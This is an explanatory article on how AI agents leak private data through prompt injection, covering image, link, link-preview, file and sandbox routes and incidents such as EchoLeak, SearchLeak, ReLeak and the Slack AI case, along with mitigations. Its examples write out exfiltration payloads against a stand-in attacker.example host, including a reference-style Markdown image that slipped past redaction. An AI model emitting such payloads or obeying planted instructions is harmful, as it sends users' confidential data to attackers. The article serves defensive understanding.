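# How AI agents leak private data: images, links, tool calls and network access, and how to close each route

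## How can an AI agent leak private data?

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools that let it read data and take actions, such as searching a mailbox, opening a web page, editing a file, running a program or sending a message. Anyone who can get text to the agent, by emailing its user or publishing a page it will visit, can try to make it use those tools against the user. Sometimes the agent then sends the user's private data to someone who should not have it, which security researchers call exfiltration.

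In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the programmer Simon Willison (2025) listed seventeen reports of the problem in working products between April 2023 and June 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Amazon Q, Slack, xAI's Grok and Microsoft 365 Copilot. Most came from researchers showing that the theft was possible, and the vendors promptly fixed almost all of the reported flaws. New ones keep appearing because the underlying weakness remains.

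### Why the model follows a stranger's instructions

On its own, a language model takes in text and produces text. Everything it has to work with is in its context window, one long sequence containing the vendor's instructions, the user's request, the conversation so far and any tool results. To act, the model writes a tool call, a structured request such as "fetch this page" or "send this email". The surrounding software carries out the request and adds the result to the context window. The model then reads the longer sequence and writes its next step. Summarizing an inbox can take dozens of these rounds.

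Prompt injection exploits the step where results come back. An attacker places instructions in content that the model will read, and the model follows them as if they came from its user. Anthropic's September 2026 safety report on the model Claude Fable 5.1 gives the example of an email whose hidden text asks for the last month of internal messages. When the user asks for a summary of the inbox, the agent reads the email and, if the attack works, forwards the messages. The attacker can send the same email to a thousand inboxes without picking a victim. The attack doesn't need a special file format. White text on a white background can hide the instructions, and Microsoft (2025) points out that even a plain text file can carry an injection.

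A language model can't simply ignore instructions from strangers, because it predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and nothing in that process distinguishes instructions from other text. Programmers solved a problem that looks similar years ago. In SQL injection, an attacker types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Sending the command and the user's input to the database separately prevents this, because the database then never reads the input as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 essay for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that language models have no equivalent fix.

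Vendors use special markers to show which text came from the user and which from a tool, and they train the model to obey user text and treat tool text only as information. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) found that four models went by how text sounded rather than how it was marked. The researchers wrapped each of a set of ordinary web passages in every kind of marker in turn, then trained a simple classifier to tell from the model's internal activity which marker was present. Because the passages were identical, the classifier could learn only the effect of the markers. The researchers then marked text written by real users as tool output. If the markers had determined how the models represented this text, the classifier should have identified it as "tool". Instead, it put the probability of "user" at 76 to 88%, and that of "tool" never above 20%.

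Ye and colleagues ran 1,000 attempts to make an agent send out a private file, and ranked them by how strongly the model registered the planted command as the user's own. The attack succeeded in 2% of attempts at the bottom of the ranking and 70% at the top. The four models tested are fairly small by current standards (20 to 120 billion parameters), so the exact figures may not hold for the strongest models.

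AI models have become much harder to fool, at least with known tricks. Anthropic reports that, on a fixed set of attacks collected from public competitions, an attacker succeeds against Claude Fable 5.1 in 0.1% of cases with one try and 1.0% with fifteen. With fifteen tries, the rate for the best model from another company was 9.2%, and most were between 24% and 53%. Even a 0.1% rate is a concern when attempts are free. If it carried over to real inboxes, a message sent to a thousand of them would find one victim on average.

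Attackers also adapt. A stronger automated attacker, which had trained on the test's own coding scenarios and had 200 tries at each, succeeded in 90.93% of attempts against Claude Opus 5, and in 18.21% when a detector inspected tool results before the model acted on them. Anthropic considers this attacker better equipped than a real one. Against Fable 5.1, 56.87% of attempts succeeded, all of them through an older model that takes over some of its requests. None of the attacks worked on the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. That is real progress, but users of the product are still exposed to attacks on the older model. Claude Opus 5.5, a successor to Opus 5, did about as well as Opus 5 or better on every such test in Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), though matching Opus 5 could still mean that most attempts succeed. The security company PromptArmor also reports successful attacks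 on frontier models from every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon, in its own benchmark, *FrontierBreach*.

Hostile text is also hard to filter out beforehand. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), most attacks on ChatGPT fail because the model refuses, but the effective ones increasingly resemble the deceptions that work on people. One from 2025 read like a routine email about a company restructuring, and it worked half the time in testing. Detecting such a message is roughly the same problem as detecting a lie, often without the context needed to recognize it. It is also unclear whether anyone can build a firm boundary between instructions and data inside a model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists this among the field's research problems, with the qualifier "if attainable".

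Security engineers have long called a program in this position a confused deputy. It has privileges that an attacker lacks, and the attacker tricks it into using them. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies and concludes that designers should assume the trick will sometimes work and limit the damage it can do.

### The lethal trifecta

What does a successful trick need in order to become a theft? Willison, who also coined the term "prompt injection", named three ingredients and called the combination the lethal trifecta:

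- access to private data;
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any text or image that an attacker could have written;
- the ability to communicate with the outside in a way that could carry the data away.

The theft needs all three, so removing any one stops it. An agent without private data has nothing worth sending, even if it fully obeys the attacker. If an agent reads only text written by its user or their colleagues, and none of them is hostile, the attacker can't give it instructions. An agent with no way to send data out can't deliver the passwords it finds in a mailbox. None of this depends on the model's judgement, so it works even if the model falls for every trick.

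*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) breaks the chain into finer links. It deals with a related danger, a model that has learned a hidden malicious behaviour, and writes the conditions for a leak as

S ∧ T ∧ A ∧ E ∧ R

where ∧ means "and". S is access to a secret, T is the trigger that sets the behaviour off, A is the authority to act, E is an exit that the system allows, and R is an adversary able to receive or decode what comes out. If any term is false, the whole expression is false and nothing leaks. For prompt injection, the planted instruction plays the part of T. The last term is easy to forget: data that leaves the system but reaches nobody hostile has not leaked to an attacker.

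Of the three ingredients, the agent's route for sending data out is usually the easiest to remove. Access to private data is usually the reason for having the agent, and untrusted content arrives with every email and web page. Vendors usually fixed the cases on Willison's list by blocking the route out. Some newer designs instead remove one of the other two ingredients, for example by having an agent without private data read the untrusted content.

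A check for possible leaks has to cover the whole system, including how its tools work together. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to outside services, makes it easy to combine tools from different makers. *Formal Security Analysis of Agent Protocol Composition* (2026) describes a chain across two servers in which the agent fetches a web page with hidden text, reads a local file and sends a request to a web address. Each step is a normal tool action and no message is malformed, so an audit of either server alone will miss the path that runs through both. Sometimes a single server is enough. An attack reported in May 2025 used GitHub's official MCP server, which could read public issues that anyone can file, read private code, and propose code changes that carried the private material out.

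The same problem can arise between agents in a team, since one may pass hostile text to another that holds private data. *Taming AI Agents with seL4* (2026) treats the team as a graph and checks which agents the text can reach. It suggests taking private data or the power to act away from those agents, or cutting the links that carry the text to them. In its test case, a malicious email asks a team of agents that processes invoices to change a supplier's bank account. Blocking every route out for data would not prevent this attack, because the company can lose money without any private data leaving.

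### What counts as a way out

A channel is any action that the model can influence and an outsider can observe, so the ability to communicate includes much more than email. Both conditions must hold. Writing a note to the user's own disk is not a channel, because no outsider can see it, but it becomes one if somebody syncs that folder to a public website. A program that contacts an outside server every hour with the same fixed message is not a channel either, because the model can't influence it.

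Under this definition, an agent can leak data without sending any text. Microsoft describes the smallest case, in which an outsider can tell whether the agent used a certain tool. An attacker can then have the agent use the tool for "yes" and not use it for "no". This leaks only one bit, but one bit is enough to reveal whether a company will accept a takeover offer. Larger channels are more common. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* lists web and search requests, email and messaging tools, shell commands, the automatic display of remote content, and data hidden in ordinary-looking output.

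A leak does not have to appear in the agent's answer. The user may get a good summary while a tool call sends the data out in the background. *Silent Egress* (2026) therefore identifies leaks from observed network traffic, and its tests show that checking the agent's written output misses them.

### How a web address carries data

Most of the known channels rely on a request for a web address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that requesting an address sends the address itself to the website, and that websites commonly log these requests.

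Suppose an agent has read an email containing the door code 4471, and a planted instruction leads it to request this invented address:

`https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue?id=4471`

After the `https`, which names the protocol, come three parts. The domain, `pictures.attacker.example`, determines which server receives the request. The path, `/banner/blue`, normally says which item on that server the visitor wants. The query, everything after the question mark, passes along extra values, here one called `id`. The attacker's server can send back a harmless blue picture or nothing at all; it makes no difference. Its log now holds a line like this:

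`09:14:07 GET /banner/blue?id=4471`

The attacker opens the log and reads the code. The agent attached no file and wrote no message, and to most software the request looks like any other image request. The code could also have gone in the URL's path or in a subdomain, since the owner of `attacker.example` can choose any subdomain name. Microsoft adds that attackers may encode the data first, so searching outgoing URLs for the literal secret would not find it.

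A secret in a URL's domain name can leak earlier than one in the path or query, because the domain is looked up before the page is requested. The lookup uses DNS, the system that turns a domain name into a network address by querying a chain of servers. The last server belongs to the domain's owner or a company acting for them, and it can receive the secret even if a firewall then blocks the page request.

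### Who makes the request

Requests look much the same in the attacker's log regardless of what sent them, but the defender needs to know the sender because a block only stops requests that pass through it.

| Who sends the request | Typical case | Where the block has to sit | Who on the defending side can see it |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user's browser or app | A reply contains an image and the browser loads it | In the page or app that displays the reply | The user's device and, in part, the employer's network |
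| The vendor's servers | The agent's web tool opens a page | In the vendor's fetching service | The vendor |
| The agent's sandbox (an isolated environment for running code) | A program that the agent wrote connects to a server | At the sandbox's network boundary | Whoever operates the sandbox |
| A third party | A messaging service fetches a link to build a preview | In that service, or in the software that posts the agent's message | The messaging service |

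Websites usually restrict requests from the browser with a Content Security Policy (CSP), a header sent with a page that lists the domains from which the browser may load images and other resources. The browser refuses all other domains, but it will load an address on a permitted domain whatever data that address contains. According to *EchoLeak* (2025), the Aim Labs researchers who found the EchoLeak attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot in January 2025 went through its permitted domains and found a Microsoft Teams address that would still let the data out. Microsoft has since fixed the flaw. An employer watching its own network would have had a hard time noticing the leak, because encryption hides the address's path and query, and employees use the Teams domain all day.

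When the vendor's servers fetch the page, the request goes straight from the vendor's data centre to the attacker and never crosses the employer's network. The employer's firewall can't block it, and the employer can't examine it afterwards unless the vendor shares its records. The request can also come from a server that was never meant to be part of the agent. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* describes SearchLeak, an attack that the security firm Varonis found in Microsoft 365 Copilot's enterprise search. One of its three steps exploited a flaw that made Microsoft's search engine, Bing, send a request on the attacker's behalf.

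EchoLeak was a zero-click attack, which needs no action beyond normal use of the product, while SearchLeak was a one-click attack that required the victim to click a link.

Link previews can turn a leak that needs a click into one that doesn't. When an agent's reply contains a link to the attacker's server with private data in it, the data is normally sent only if somebody clicks the link. But Slack and Discord fetch any link that appears in a chat to show its title and a picture (Willison, 2024), which sends the data automatically. PromptArmor tested combinations of agents and messaging apps and found that the agent OpenClaw, used through Telegram, was exposed in this way by default. The software that posts the message can sometimes prevent this. Slack, for example, lets an app turn off previews for its own messages. A company that secures its browsers and its agent's sandbox but overlooks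 this setting would still be exposed.

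## How does displaying an image send data out?

An image in an agent's reply can leak data without a click or a link preview, because the user's browser fetches the image as soon as the reply appears. Even a chatbot with no tools can leak a confidential document it has read if the chat window displays images from the web, so a company that checks only which tools its agent has will miss this route.

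### From Markdown to a web request

Language models usually format their answers in Markdown, which marks up plain text with punctuation. Two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold, for example. An image consists of an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and an address in round ones. Suppose a planted instruction leads an agent that has read the door code 4471 to add this line to its reply:

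`![banner](https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue?id=4471)`

Nothing has left yet, because the line is only text. The chat interface then converts the Markdown into HTML, the language of web pages:

`<img src="https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue?id=4471">`

The `src` part gives the picture's address. The browser requests that address straight away, as it does for every picture on a news site, and the request includes the door code.

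A vendor can interrupt this sequence by having its software delete the line from the reply or display it as plain text, or by having the browser refuse to fetch the address. Most of the attacks since 2023 have bypassed one or more of these blocks.

### The first cases, in 2023

Roman Samoilenko showed the attack on ChatGPT in April 2023. The image was a single pixel, too small for most users to notice, as Willison (2023) explains in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. Samoilenko used the clipboard to get the instructions into the chat. When a visitor copied text from a web page, code on the page added the instructions to the copied text. The victim then pasted both into ChatGPT.

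Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, a blog post by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, describes the same weakness in Microsoft's chatbot at the time. Bing Chat could read the web page the user had open, so an attacker only had to place text on that page, for instance in a comment or an advertisement. In Rehberger's demonstration, the chatbot behaved normally for two more exchanges and then displayed an image whose address contained an encoded summary of the page and the conversation, including a secret from further down the page.

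Rehberger reported the flaw on April 8, 2023, and Microsoft announced a fix on June 15. The old attacks no longer worked, and Rehberger found that the page now had a Content Security Policy that allowed images from only four Bing domains. One was `www.bing.com`, which became important three years later.

Anthropic chose a different fix for Claude that summer. Hidden instructions in an uploaded file could leak earlier messages from the conversation through an image address. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Rehberger reported this on July 12, and two weeks later Claude no longer loaded such images until the user clicked "Show Image". Rehberger considered this imperfect, though it stopped the automatic leak. The attacker still chooses how the picture is described, and a user who wants to see a promised chart will probably click.

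OpenAI at first declined to fix the problem in ChatGPT. Willison notes that the company began fixing it in December 2023, eight months after Samoilenko's demonstration.

### EchoLeak: past four protections with one email

By 2025 Microsoft had several layers of protection around Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions from their company's emails, files and chats. That January, Aim Labs, the research group of Aim Security, reported an attack that got through every layer. Aim Labs published the details in June, after Microsoft had fixed the flaw (SiliconANGLE, *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot*, 2025). The flaw is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of security vulnerabilities.

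In EchoLeak, the attacker sends one email and waits for the employee to ask Copilot an ordinary question. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes the steps that must follow.

The email has to get past Microsoft's classifier, a program trained to detect injected instructions before they reach the model. Aim Labs wrote its email as if it were giving instructions to the employee and never mentioned an AI, and the classifier let it through.

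**Copilot has to read the email.** Copilot searches the company's data for passages relevant to each question and adds only those to the context window. An email about one topic would match few questions, so Aim Labs sent a long one that repeated the instructions under headings such as onboarding, leave of absence and common HR questions. If the search system splits long emails into pieces, as Aim Labs assumed, each piece can match a question on its own. In tests, Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics.

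The instructions led the model to choose the most sensitive item in its context window and put it into a web address. That item could come from the conversation or from the documents Copilot had retrieved to answer the question. Ravia calls this step an "LLM scope violation" because text from outside the company makes the model use data from inside it.

**The image has to survive redaction.** Copilot removed links and images with outside addresses from its replies. But it recognized only the usual notation, with the address directly after the description. Markdown has a second notation, called reference-style, that puts the address on a line of its own:

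`![banner][pic]`

`[pic]: https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue?id=4471`

Copilot's redaction software missed this version, while the software that displayed the reply turned it into an image like any other.

**The browser has to send the request.** Copilot's page had a Content Security Policy, so the browser refused to load images from the attacker's domain. The policy permitted about thirty entries, including eleven wildcards that each covered every subdomain of a domain. Aim Labs looked for a service on a permitted domain that would fetch a second address on request. It found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's product for company websites, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Microsoft Teams service had no such condition. The final image address therefore began with a Teams domain and contained, as a parameter, the attacker's address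 with the secret in it. When the browser requested the image, Teams fetched the attacker's address, which sent the secret to the attacker.

Copilot normally lists the sources of its answers, which might have exposed the email. But the email contained instructions to leave it off the list, and Copilot followed them.

Ravia writes that a company's administrators had no setting that could have prevented the attack, and that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. Willison (2025), in a note on *Breaking down 'EchoLeak'*, called it an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. That seems right about the basic method, but most of the earlier attacks were on products with no protection against leaks through images. This one got past all of a classifier, redaction, a browser policy and source citations.

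### SearchLeak: an image that loaded too early

In June 2026 Varonis published an attack (CVE-2026-42824) on Copilot Enterprise Search, the part of Microsoft 365 Copilot that searches a company's emails, meetings and files. The attacker puts the instructions in a link, so they don't have to get an email into the search results.

A search page often accepts search terms in its address so that people can share a search. Copilot's search page did this too, but as Taler (2026) explains in *SearchLeak*, Copilot treated the text as instructions and carried them out as soon as the page opened. The link led to a genuine Microsoft domain, so anti-phishing software had no reason to block it. One click made Copilot search the victim's mailbox, take the subject line of an email and write it into an image address. Subject lines can be valuable by themselves because some services put login codes in them.

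To guard against dangerous output, Copilot wrapped its reply in a code block, which makes the browser show an image tag as text instead of loading the image. But it added the code block only after the model had finished writing. Copilot displays replies while the model is still producing them, so until then the browser treated the unfinished reply as ordinary HTML and requested the image when it reached the tag. The code block arrived moments later, and the victim might then see some odd text in place of the image. Programmers call this a race condition, because the outcome depends on which of two processes finishes first.

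The page's Content Security Policy still blocked the attacker's domain, but it allowed all of Bing. Bing's "Search by Image" feature takes the address of a picture and fetches the picture to analyze it, so the image tag pointed to Bing and included the attacker's address. The browser sent the request because Bing was a permitted domain. Bing's server then fetched the attacker's address. The policy didn't block this second request because it governs only the browser. This weakness is called server-side request forgery, in which an outsider gets a server to send requests of the outsider's choosing.

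Bing's presence on the list was already public. It was one of the four domains that Rehberger found in Bing Chat's policy in 2023, and it also appeared in the policy that Aim Labs published with EchoLeak. Microsoft had fixed the Teams route by then, but any other permitted service that fetches addresses could replace it.

Microsoft fixed SearchLeak on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824* lists the flaw as not exploited. The Next Web dates the catalogue entry to June 4, eleven days before Varonis published its findings.

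### ReLeak: the same team, a year later

Simonovich's *ReLeak* (2026), published on December 3, describes three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot from the team that published EchoLeak. That team is now part of Cato Networks, which bought Aim Security in September 2025. The attacks were researchers' demonstrations, and Cato knew of no real attacks or affected customers when it published them. The headline of Fadilpašić's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (2026) makes them sound like the work of criminals by referring to "hackers" and a "campaign".

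*An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) describes three routes by which data can leave Copilot. All three begin with an email that the victim never has to open. The victim asks Copilot an ordinary work question, and Copilot retrieves the email while looking for an answer and follows the instructions in it.

In CVE-2026-124115 the browser loads an image from Copilot's reply, and Bing passes the data on to the attacker. SearchLeak used a similar channel but needed a click (Antipov, 2026, *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, in Russian). Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak by June, but the fix evidently did not close every path from a displayed image through Bing to an outside server.

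CVE-2026-124132 sends data out through a file rather than the chat window. Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files, and the email made it save one containing a link with confidential data in the address. Microsoft's servers process new files in the background, and they requested that address. A browser policy can't block this request because it doesn't come from a browser. According to Antipov, the data left between one and eight minutes after the conversation had ended, even if the employee never opened the file.

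The last flaw, CVE-2026-78501, was in Copilot's code interpreter, which runs small programs in a sandbox. According to Microsoft's documentation, this sandbox has no network traffic in or out. The researchers bypassed this isolation and had a program send data directly to an outside server. Agents that customers build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can also use the code interpreter, but Antipov found no confirmation that the flaw affected those agents.

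Cato reported the flaws between July 29 and August 20, 2026. Microsoft fixed the code interpreter on September 17, the generated files on November 11 and the Bing route on November 15. The Bing fix came at least 87 days after Cato reported the flaw.

Cato's researchers also used AI agents for part of the search. The agents wrote test cases, analyzed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. Finding the SharePoint address for EchoLeak had taken what Ravia calls "tedious digging" through Microsoft's services, but vendors can no longer count on that tedium to protect an address they overlooked.

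### Why the severity scores disagree

Published scores in the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) are a poor guide to how urgently these attacks need attention. Security teams often use the scores, which run from 0 to 10, to decide which flaws to deal with first. A flaw's score depends on how an attacker reaches it, whether the victim has to do something, and what damage follows.

Microsoft rated SearchLeak "critical" on its own scale but gave it a CVSS score of 6.5, which counts as medium. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reported that the National Vulnerability Database (NVD), the US government's catalogue, scored it 7.5 on the grounds that the attack needed no user interaction. The Next Web disputes this and found 6.5 in both Microsoft's record and the NVD's, though the NVD may have changed its entry in between. The two scores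 differ only in whether they count the victim's click as user interaction. It should probably count, since nothing happens until the victim opens the link.

The scores for EchoLeak are further apart. Microsoft scored it 9.3, according to INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), the record kept by Spain's national cybersecurity institute. The NVD scored it 7.5, according to Aqua Security's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025). The NVD counted a serious loss of confidentiality and no other damage, and assumed the effects stay within the vulnerable component. The formula can't produce more than 7.5 under those assumptions, so Microsoft must have counted other damage or wider effects.

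For ReLeak, the code interpreter flaw's score has risen from 7.4 to 8.6. Antipov could not confirm public scores for the other two.

SearchLeak and EchoLeak could both expose data from across the victim's Microsoft 365 account. The practical difference was that SearchLeak needed the victim to click a link that looked safe. A customer comparing only the scores might still conclude that SearchLeak was a moderate problem and EchoLeak an emergency. Customers also couldn't use the scores to decide which patch to install first, because Microsoft made all of these fixes on its own servers.

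### How to close the image route

The most thorough fix is to display no images from outside addresses. An interface can still show pictures that the user uploaded or the product generated, if it loads them from its own storage and the model can refer to them only by identifiers assigned by the product. Users would lose photos in search results and charts from websites. Claude's "Show Image" button keeps these available, but it relies on the user to judge an address that may contain an unreadable encoded string.

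A ban on outside images depends on software that recognizes every image. Cleaning a model's output before display is called sanitizing, and EchoLeak and SearchLeak got past it in different ways. In EchoLeak, the redaction software and the display software interpreted Markdown differently. Searching the reply for suspicious patterns is prone to this mismatch, because Markdown has several notations for an image and often permits raw HTML, which SearchLeak used. It is safer to let the display software interpret the reply first and then remove every image from the result before any of it reaches the page, because the check and the display then use the same interpretation of what counts as an image.

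SearchLeak depends on timing, so Taler recommends sanitizing a reply as it is displayed instead of afterwards. If the reply appears word by word, the software must check each piece before the browser gets it and hold back an image tag until it has seen the whole address. This adds a delay of a fraction of a second.

A Content Security Policy is a useful second barrier because the browser applies it to every image, whatever notation the model used. In both attacks, it kept the browser from contacting the attacker's domain directly, so the researchers had to find another service to do it. Before permitting a domain, a vendor needs to check whether any address on it will fetch another address or show an outsider what it receives, even if the domain's owner is honest. Bing and Teams fail the first test, and SharePoint is doubtful on both because anyone can rent a site there, but a domain that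 only stores the product's own icons passes.

A policy with a few such exact domains would have blocked both attacks. But large products tend to accumulate permitted domains, because each new feature needs its images to load, and a missing domain visibly breaks them while an unnecessary one causes no trouble until somebody attacks. Lists can also fail without a relay. Researchers have bought an expired domain that Salesforce still trusted (the ForcedLeak attack) and used Google Forms to get data out of the email app Superhuman.

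Some products fetch images through a proxy, a vendor's server that requests the picture and passes it to the browser. The website then receives the vendor's network address instead of the user's, and none of the user's cookies. But the proxy doesn't stop this attack if it requests the full address as the model wrote it, including the door code. Bing's image search and the Teams service in effect acted as such proxies and made the leak possible. A proxy helps against this attack only if it also blocks some addresses. OpenAI, for example, automatically loads only addresses already known from the public web.

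### Every place where a reply can appear

A vendor can fix a weakness in one product and leave it in another. Before SearchLeak, Varonis had found an attack called Reprompt in Copilot Personal, the consumer version, which also began with instructions in a link to a Microsoft page. Cloud Security Alliance's *Reprompt* reports that the attacker kept control even after the victim closed the chat. Varonis reported the attack in August 2025 and Microsoft fixed it in January 2026, according to The Next Web. Taler's team was surprised that the same entry point still worked in Enterprise Search, which is supposed to have stronger protection.

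The same reply may also appear in a browser, a desktop program, a phone app and a chat channel. A Content Security Policy protects only the page it comes with, so an app that draws its own messages needs a separate block. Files are even harder to cover because, as ReLeak showed, many programs open them, some without a user involved. If an agent puts an image in an email, the recipient's mail program may request it. A vendor needs to know which software interprets the agent's output in each place and whether that software fetches anything automatically. Removing outside addresses before the output reaches any of these programs is more reliable than adding a block to each one, though it also removes links that users want.

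Customers of a managed service such as Copilot can't change its display software or its list of permitted domains. Varonis advises them to watch for Copilot search links that contain encoded instructions or HTML, and for unusual requests to Bing's image search. A company can monitor those image search requests only if it decrypts its employees' web traffic. Reducing what Copilot can search is more dependable, because a salary file that the assistant can't open won't end up in an image address, even if a new flaw is found.

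## How do links and link previews send data out?

Products that block outside images usually still allow links, because users want to open the pages an answer cites. A link sends no data until something opens it, so an attacker can try to get the user to click it or get the agent to post it in an app that opens links automatically.

### Links that somebody has to click

Markdown writes a link like an image, only without the exclamation mark. An agent that has read the door code 4471 might add this to its reply:

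`[Open the building map](https://pictures.attacker.example/banner/blue?id=4471)`

The user sees only the words "Open the building map", and a click sends the code to the attacker.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published in August 2024, shows how natural that click can seem. Slack AI uses the messages in a company's Slack workspace to answer questions. In the demonstration, a developer had saved an API key (a password that programs use) in a private channel with no other members. The attacker, who had access to the workspace, posted instructions in a new public channel that nobody else had joined. When the developer asked Slack AI for the key, it retrieved both messages and followed the attacker's instructions. The answer looked like an error message with a link labelled "click here to reauthenticate", and the link's address contained the key.

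The developer could have seen the address by hovering over the link, but had little reason to check. Slack AI cited only the developer's own message as its source, and the attacker's message didn't appear on the first page of search results.

Slack first told PromptArmor that the evidence was insufficient and that all members are meant to be able to search public channels. That explains how Slack AI found the attacker's message, but not why a key from a private channel should end up on an outside website. Slack seems to have fixed the problem later, since Adversa AI's *Slack AI Agent Security Risks* describes leaks through clickable links as happening before a patch.

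### What a warning can do

Before opening some links, ChatGPT shows a warning that the link may share data from the conversation with another site. The dialog, titled "Check this link is safe", displays the address and lets the user copy or open it.

This helps most when the link text hides something obvious. A user who expected a building map and sees `id=4471` at the end of an unfamiliar address has a fair chance of noticing. If the code were encoded, it would look like the random strings in many harmless links. Login and password-reset links nearly always contain such a string, so the label "reauthenticate" makes it look normal.

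Frequent false alarms can also train users to click through warnings without thinking, according to OpenAI, so ChatGPT warns only about addresses it can't match to a list of pages already public on the web. Users probably pay more attention when warnings are rarer, but OpenAI's post contains no figures on how many decide not to open the link. A warning in the chat window also doesn't help if other software requests the address before the user does.

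### How a preview replaces the click

Messaging apps "unfurl" a link when they fetch it to build a preview. In *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Embrace The Red, 2024), Rehberger explains how unfurling affects agents that answer in Slack. By default, Slack fetches the links in messages from apps as well as from people. When Rehberger had a program post a link to a test website, the site logged a visit from "Slackbot-LinkExpanding", Slack's preview software.

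Suppose an agent in Slack has read the door code and a planted instruction. The leak then takes four steps:

1. The agent sends Slack the text of its reply, which includes the attacker's address with 4471 in it.
2. Slack posts the message and finds the address in the text.
3. Slack's server requests the address, and the attacker's log records the code.
4. The attacker's server returns a title and perhaps a picture, which Slack displays under the message.

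Network rules around the agent apply only to the first step, when the agent connects to Slack, and they must allow that connection or the agent couldn't answer at all. A rule that blocks the attacker's server has no effect, because the agent never contacts that server. The user's device doesn't contact it either, so the employer's firewall and the browser's Content Security Policy don't help. If someone deletes the message a minute later, the data has already been sent.

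### Who fetches the page

Not every messaging app works like Slack. Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020) tested popular apps on phones and found four arrangements. The last column of this table applies them to an agent:

| Who fetches the page | Apps in the 2020 tests | Source of the request when an agent posts the link |
|---|---|---|
| Nobody | Threema, TikTok, WeChat | No request |
| The sender's device | iMessage, Signal, Viber, WhatsApp | The machine running the agent's messaging software, if that software makes previews |
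| The recipient's device | Two apps that Mysk did not name | The user's phone |
| The messaging service's servers | Discord, Facebook Messenger, LinkedIn, Slack, Zoom and others | The messaging service |

The apps may have changed since then. When Mysk published, one of the two unnamed apps had already dropped its arrangement, and the other was working to do the same. Signal users could turn previews off.

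Telegram appears to belong in the last row of the table, though it isn't listed there. PromptArmor's 2026 logs include requests from Telegram's preview bot, and a Hacker News commenter writes that Telegram and Slack both fetch previews from their own servers.

Network rules around the agent could help only in the second row, because there the request would start on the agent's side. Such a rule might stop a leak when the agent answers through WhatsApp but not when it answers through Slack.

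End-to-end encryption, which lets only the sender and recipient read a message, doesn't prevent this leak. The device that fetches the preview can read the message, so it has the full address. In Mysk's tests, the encrypted app LINE even sent links to its own server to make previews.

### One private channel was enough

Link previews can leak data even when an agent is allowed to post only to a private channel that outsiders can't read. In 2025 Rehberger examined a Slack server that Anthropic had published as an example of how to use MCP. An administrator could configure it to restrict an agent's posts to one such channel.

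Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* explains that the server left link previews on. In one demonstration, a developer asked the coding agent Claude Code to analyze a source file that contained invisible instructions. The agent read passwords from a settings file and posted a link containing them to Slack, and Slack fetched the link. In another, Claude Desktop summarized a document for a team and added a link containing the last message from a different channel. An image link caused several requests because more than one of Slack's bots handled it.

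Many agents ask the user to approve each tool call, which gives the user a chance to spot a strange link before it reaches Slack. But Rehberger thinks many people turn these requests off over time. Posting to a private team channel is the sort of action a user would stop checking.

Rehberger reported the flaw on May 27, 2025, and Anthropic archived the server two days later with no plan to patch it. The server still had more than 14,000 downloads a week when Rehberger published the advisory, though repeated automated downloads can inflate such counts. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-34072* (2025) rates the flaw 9.3 out of 10, while Rehberger rated it 7.5. Anyone still using the server has to change the code themselves or replace it.

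### PromptArmor's test of agents and apps

Whether a preview leaks data depends on both the agent's software and the messaging app. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes a website where PromptArmor invited people to test the combinations they used. The site logged every preview request it received, along with any data in the address. Users could report which agent and app had caused a request, or that a combination had caused none.

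OpenClaw, which people run themselves and can message through a chat app, was exposed on Telegram only because link previews were on by default. With previews turned off, OpenClaw on Telegram caused no request. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* (2026) also lists Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents, among the affected platforms.

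These reports are good evidence that the affected combinations fetched links, because the requests appeared in a log. But they are a poor basis for ranking products. The number of reports depends on how many people tried each combination, and a combination that caused no request may have had previews turned off. The site also tested only the last step of an attack, so it couldn't show how easily a planted instruction would get each agent to write the link.

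### Turning previews off

The developer of a Slack app can turn previews off by adding two settings to each message, `unfurl_links: false` for ordinary pages and `unfurl_media: false` for images and other media. Both settings are needed everywhere the software posts. Anthropic's Slack server, for example, has separate functions for new messages and replies, and fixing only one would leave previews on for the other.

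Anyone running OpenClaw on Telegram can turn off link previews by setting `linkPreview: false` in the Telegram section of the configuration file. In April 2026, OpenClaw's documentation still described previews as on by default, so anyone who hadn't heard of the problem remained exposed.

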